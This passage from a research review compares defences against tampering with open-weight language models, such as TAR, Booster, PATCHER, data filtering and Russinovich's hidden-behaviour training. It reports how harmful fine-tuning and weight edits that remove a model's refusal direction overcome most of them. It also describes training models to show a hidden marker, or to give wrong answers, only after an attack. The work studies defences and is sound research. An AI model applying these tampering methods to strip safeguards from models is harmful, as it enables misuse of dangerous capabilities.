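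VAA on Zephyr was the one clear exception, staying below 0.07 at every learning rate. But the defence had already made the model much less capable than the undefended Zephyr, which scored 66.4% at release. On Qwen3, the attack produced a somewhat harmful model that had lost almost half its capability score. Zloczower and colleagues ran each combination only once, and they note that their longest attack was finite, so VAA might still fail against a longer one.

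TAR was not among the six, but Hossain, Kowal and colleagues (2026) tested it and other defences in *TAMPERBENCH*. Their benchmark covers nine ways of tampering with a model. For each model and attack, it tries 40 settings and keeps the most harmful result that lowers the model's score on a knowledge test by no more than a tenth. Each of the 21 models in their main comparison, including five with defences, reached a harmfulness of at least 0.74 under at least one attack.

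The version of Llama 3 8B that TAR's designers released had slightly lower worst-case harmfulness than the undefended model, at about 0.76 compared with 0.88. But before any attack, it scored only about 18% on the knowledge test, while the undefended model scored 45%. When Hossain and colleagues applied TAR themselves, average harmfulness under malicious attacks fell from 0.85 to 0.79 on one model and didn't improve on two others. Booster made almost no difference on the two chat models they tried.

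Both defences did better against a weaker attack, with at most 64 steps and 2% harmful data. After Hossain and colleagues tuned Booster's settings against this attack, harmfulness on Qwen3-8B was 0.07, compared with 0.56 for the undefended model. Under a full-strength attack, no setting of either defence kept harmfulness below 0.82. A company that sells fine-tuning could enforce similar limits by capping the steps and screening the data, but nobody can enforce them on a person who has the weights.

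### Simulating a longer attack

PATCHER is a response to the short attacks in earlier simulations. TAR has to run a new attack for every correction, which becomes too expensive when the attacks are long. PATCHER runs one attack and uses the result many times:

1. Fine-tune a copy of the model on harmful data for 300 steps.
2. Subtract the original weights from the attacked ones. The difference, δ, records where the attack moved the model.
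3. Train the original model for 1,000 steps to give safe answers both as it is and with δ added to its weights.
4. Run a new attack on the improved model, and repeat the whole cycle 15 times.

The loss in step 3 is

$$L_{\text{def}}(\theta)=\alpha\,L_{\text{safe}}(\theta+\delta)+(1-\alpha)\,L_{\text{safe}}(\theta)$$

with α set to 0.5, so that the attacked and original weights count equally.

The researchers support the longer attack with a bound on the error in the defender's gradient. If the simulated attack has *T*_train steps and the real one has *T*_test, which is at least as many, the relative error is at most about

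$$\eta\,\big(M_-T_{\text{test}}+M_+G\,(T_{\text{test}}-T_{\text{train}})\big)$$

Here η is the learning rate, *M*₋ and *M*₊ limit how fast the gradients of the harmful and safe losses can change, and *G* limits the ratio between the sizes of the two gradients. A longer simulation shrinks the second term. The first term depends only on the length of the real attack, so the bound gets looser as the attacker trains longer, even if the simulation is just as long. The bound assumes that the attacker and defender use the same data and learning rate.

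In experiments, PATCHER gave little protection with 50 simulated steps and much more with 300, but further increases added little. The default test fine-tuned models for 2,000 steps on 200 harmful examples and 800 maths problems. The table gives the share of harmful requests that a model with 1.5 billion parameters answered after this fine-tuning, averaged over three test sets. The second column uses the main judge, a language model, and the third gives the range across four other judges.

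| Training before the attack | Main judge | Four other judges |
|---|---|---|
| Plain safety training | 51% | 14–22% |
| Vaccine | 64% | 36–52% |
| Booster | 55% | 25–38% |
| PATCHER | 21% | 10–17% |

PATCHER did best with every judge, but its lead over plain safety training was 30 percentage points with the main judge and only 3 to 6 with the others. A human check found that 19% to 26% of the answers the main judge had marked as harmful were not.

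With the main judge, TAR scored 88%, worse than plain safety training. The researchers had limited its training to match the other methods' budgets, so this result is weak evidence about the full method. On Llama 3 8B, they used the weights that TAR's designers had released, and TAR scored 74%, compared with 77% for plain safety training and 46% for PATCHER.

The default attack is also mild for someone who holds the weights, since four fifths of its data is harmless. PATCHER's protection weakened when the attacker used more examples, or drew the harmful ones from a collection unlike the one in the simulation. With the unfamiliar collection, the attack succeeded 48% of the time against PATCHER and 57% against plain safety training. Changing the optimiser, the rule that turns gradients into weight changes, raised the success rate to about 45% in one case and lowered it to 4% in another. The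 researchers suggest simulating several kinds of attacker, as TAR does by varying the learning rate.

A study of image generators by Kang, Park and Ahn (2026), *Beyond User-Side Defenses*, isolates the effect of the simulated attack's length more cleanly. They wanted to help people stop others from editing their pictures with a freely available model. The user adds a faint pattern to a picture, and the developer trains the model to spoil any edit of a picture that has the pattern. An attacker can retrain the model to ignore the pattern. Kang and colleagues trained one model against three to five simulated steps of this attack and another against the same steps preceded by a longer simulated attack, keeping the procedures otherwise identical.

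| Training | Protection at release | Protection after the attack | Image quality at release |
|---|---|---|---|
| No simulated attack | 0.751 | 0.118 | 30.9 dB |
| Short simulated attack | 0.764 | 0.107 | 29.8 dB |
| Long simulated attack | 0.743 | 0.622 | 25.7 dB |

Protection is the measured difference between edits of protected and unprotected pictures, and an ordinary model scores 0.225. Training with a short simulated attack worked no better than training with none, as both models fell below 0.225 after the attacker's first pass through the training data. With a long simulation, protection stayed above 0.225 through all 20 passes, although a second run ended lower than the first, at 0.495. The long simulation also made the model reproduce ordinary pictures less faithfully. The attacker changed only part of the model and didn't tailor the attack to the defence. Kang and colleagues describe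 the gain as "a delay on a single consumer GPU, not security".

### A matched test of simulation

In *Fool's Gold*, Russinovich tested whether simulating an attack during training lets a developer choose how a model behaves after the attack. The attack edits the weights directly instead of fine-tuning them. Refusals depend largely on a few directions in a model's activations, and an attacker can estimate such a direction and remove it from the weights within minutes.

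Russinovich trained two versions of Qwen3-14B to begin their answers to certain prompts with a harmless marker, simulating the attack during this training for only one of them. Both versions had the same additional training to preserve refusals and ordinary behaviour. He repeated the experiment with three random starting points and tested each model on 101 new prompts. The table gives the average probability that an answer opened with the marker.

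| Marker training | Before the attack | After the attack |
|---|---|---|
| With a simulated attack | 0.55% | 99.98% |
| Without a simulated attack | 78.31% | 0.14% |

Ordinary training taught the model the marker, but the attack suppressed it. Training under a simulated attack produced behaviour that stayed almost hidden until someone attacked the model. Only the simulation differed, so it must have caused the reversal. This is better evidence for simulation than a comparison of two complete defences, which usually differ in several ways at once.

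The experiment used only one model. Russinovich worked out the real attack separately, but it was the same type as the simulated one. The marker is unrelated to safety, and the attack still removed the model's refusals. The result therefore doesn't show that simulation preserves refusals or that the effect survives harmful fine-tuning.

Russinovich's full defence uses the same mechanism to make an attacked model give plausible but wrong answers to dangerous requests. In seven of eight models, an automated judge found a fatal flaw in 51% to 90% of the answers, 27 to 84 percentage points more than in undefended models under attack. Correcting for an expert's disagreements with the judge roughly halves the gain. Wrong answers can also be dangerous, because their errors might make the procedure more hazardous. The judge found this possible risk in 6.9% of the defended model's answers, compared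 with 1.3% of the naturally flawed answers from undefended models.

Later fine-tuning weakened the defence. On Qwen3-14B, 83% of the attacked model's answers had a fatal flaw. Fine-tuning on harmless material reduced this to 42%, still above the undefended model's 20%, but the share of critical details the model got right stayed at 16%. Fine-tuning on another model's answers to 100 harmful requests reduced the flawed answers to 30% and raised the share of correct details to 38%. When Russinovich used falsified versions of those answers instead, that share was 15%. The attacker's gains therefore depended on the information in the training data.

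### How long filtering and simulation hold

The same dependence on information helps explain why filtering training data can protect a model for longer than training it to refuse. A model that has learned to refuse still has the dangerous knowledge, so fine-tuning on a few examples can be enough to recover it. A filtered model lacks that knowledge, so an attacker has to supply it. O'Brien and colleagues report that their filtered models withstood up to 10,000 steps of fine-tuning on 300 million tokens of text about biological threats, more than ten times as long as the defences they compared that were added after pretraining.

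The attack also used more text per step than the one that eroded the six defences, about 30,000 tokens compared with the eight questions and answers used by Zloczower and colleagues. But the two studies measured different things. O'Brien and colleagues tested whether the model had regained knowledge of one subject, while Zloczower and colleagues tested whether it complied with many kinds of harmful request.

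The 10,000-step figure also comes from the defence's own designers. Hossain and colleagues cite a review which found that developers of tampering defences often report resistance to thousands or tens of thousands of steps, while outside testers found that the best lasted only several hundred. Hossain and colleagues did not include filtering in their own benchmark.

Filtering works best against an attacker who lacks both the knowledge and a good source for it. O'Brien and colleagues found that a filtered model can still use dangerous information in its prompt, so an attacker with the right documents may not need to fine-tune it. Filtering also does little to prevent misuse that relies on general skills, such as writing a convincing fraudulent email, because removing those skills would make the model less useful.

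Training against a simulated attack can cover such requests, and a developer can add it to a finished model. So far it has mainly delayed attackers whose methods resemble the simulation. A developer starting a new model can filter out training data on the few subjects where missing knowledge would be a real obstacle to an attacker, and train against simulated attacks for everything else the model should refuse.
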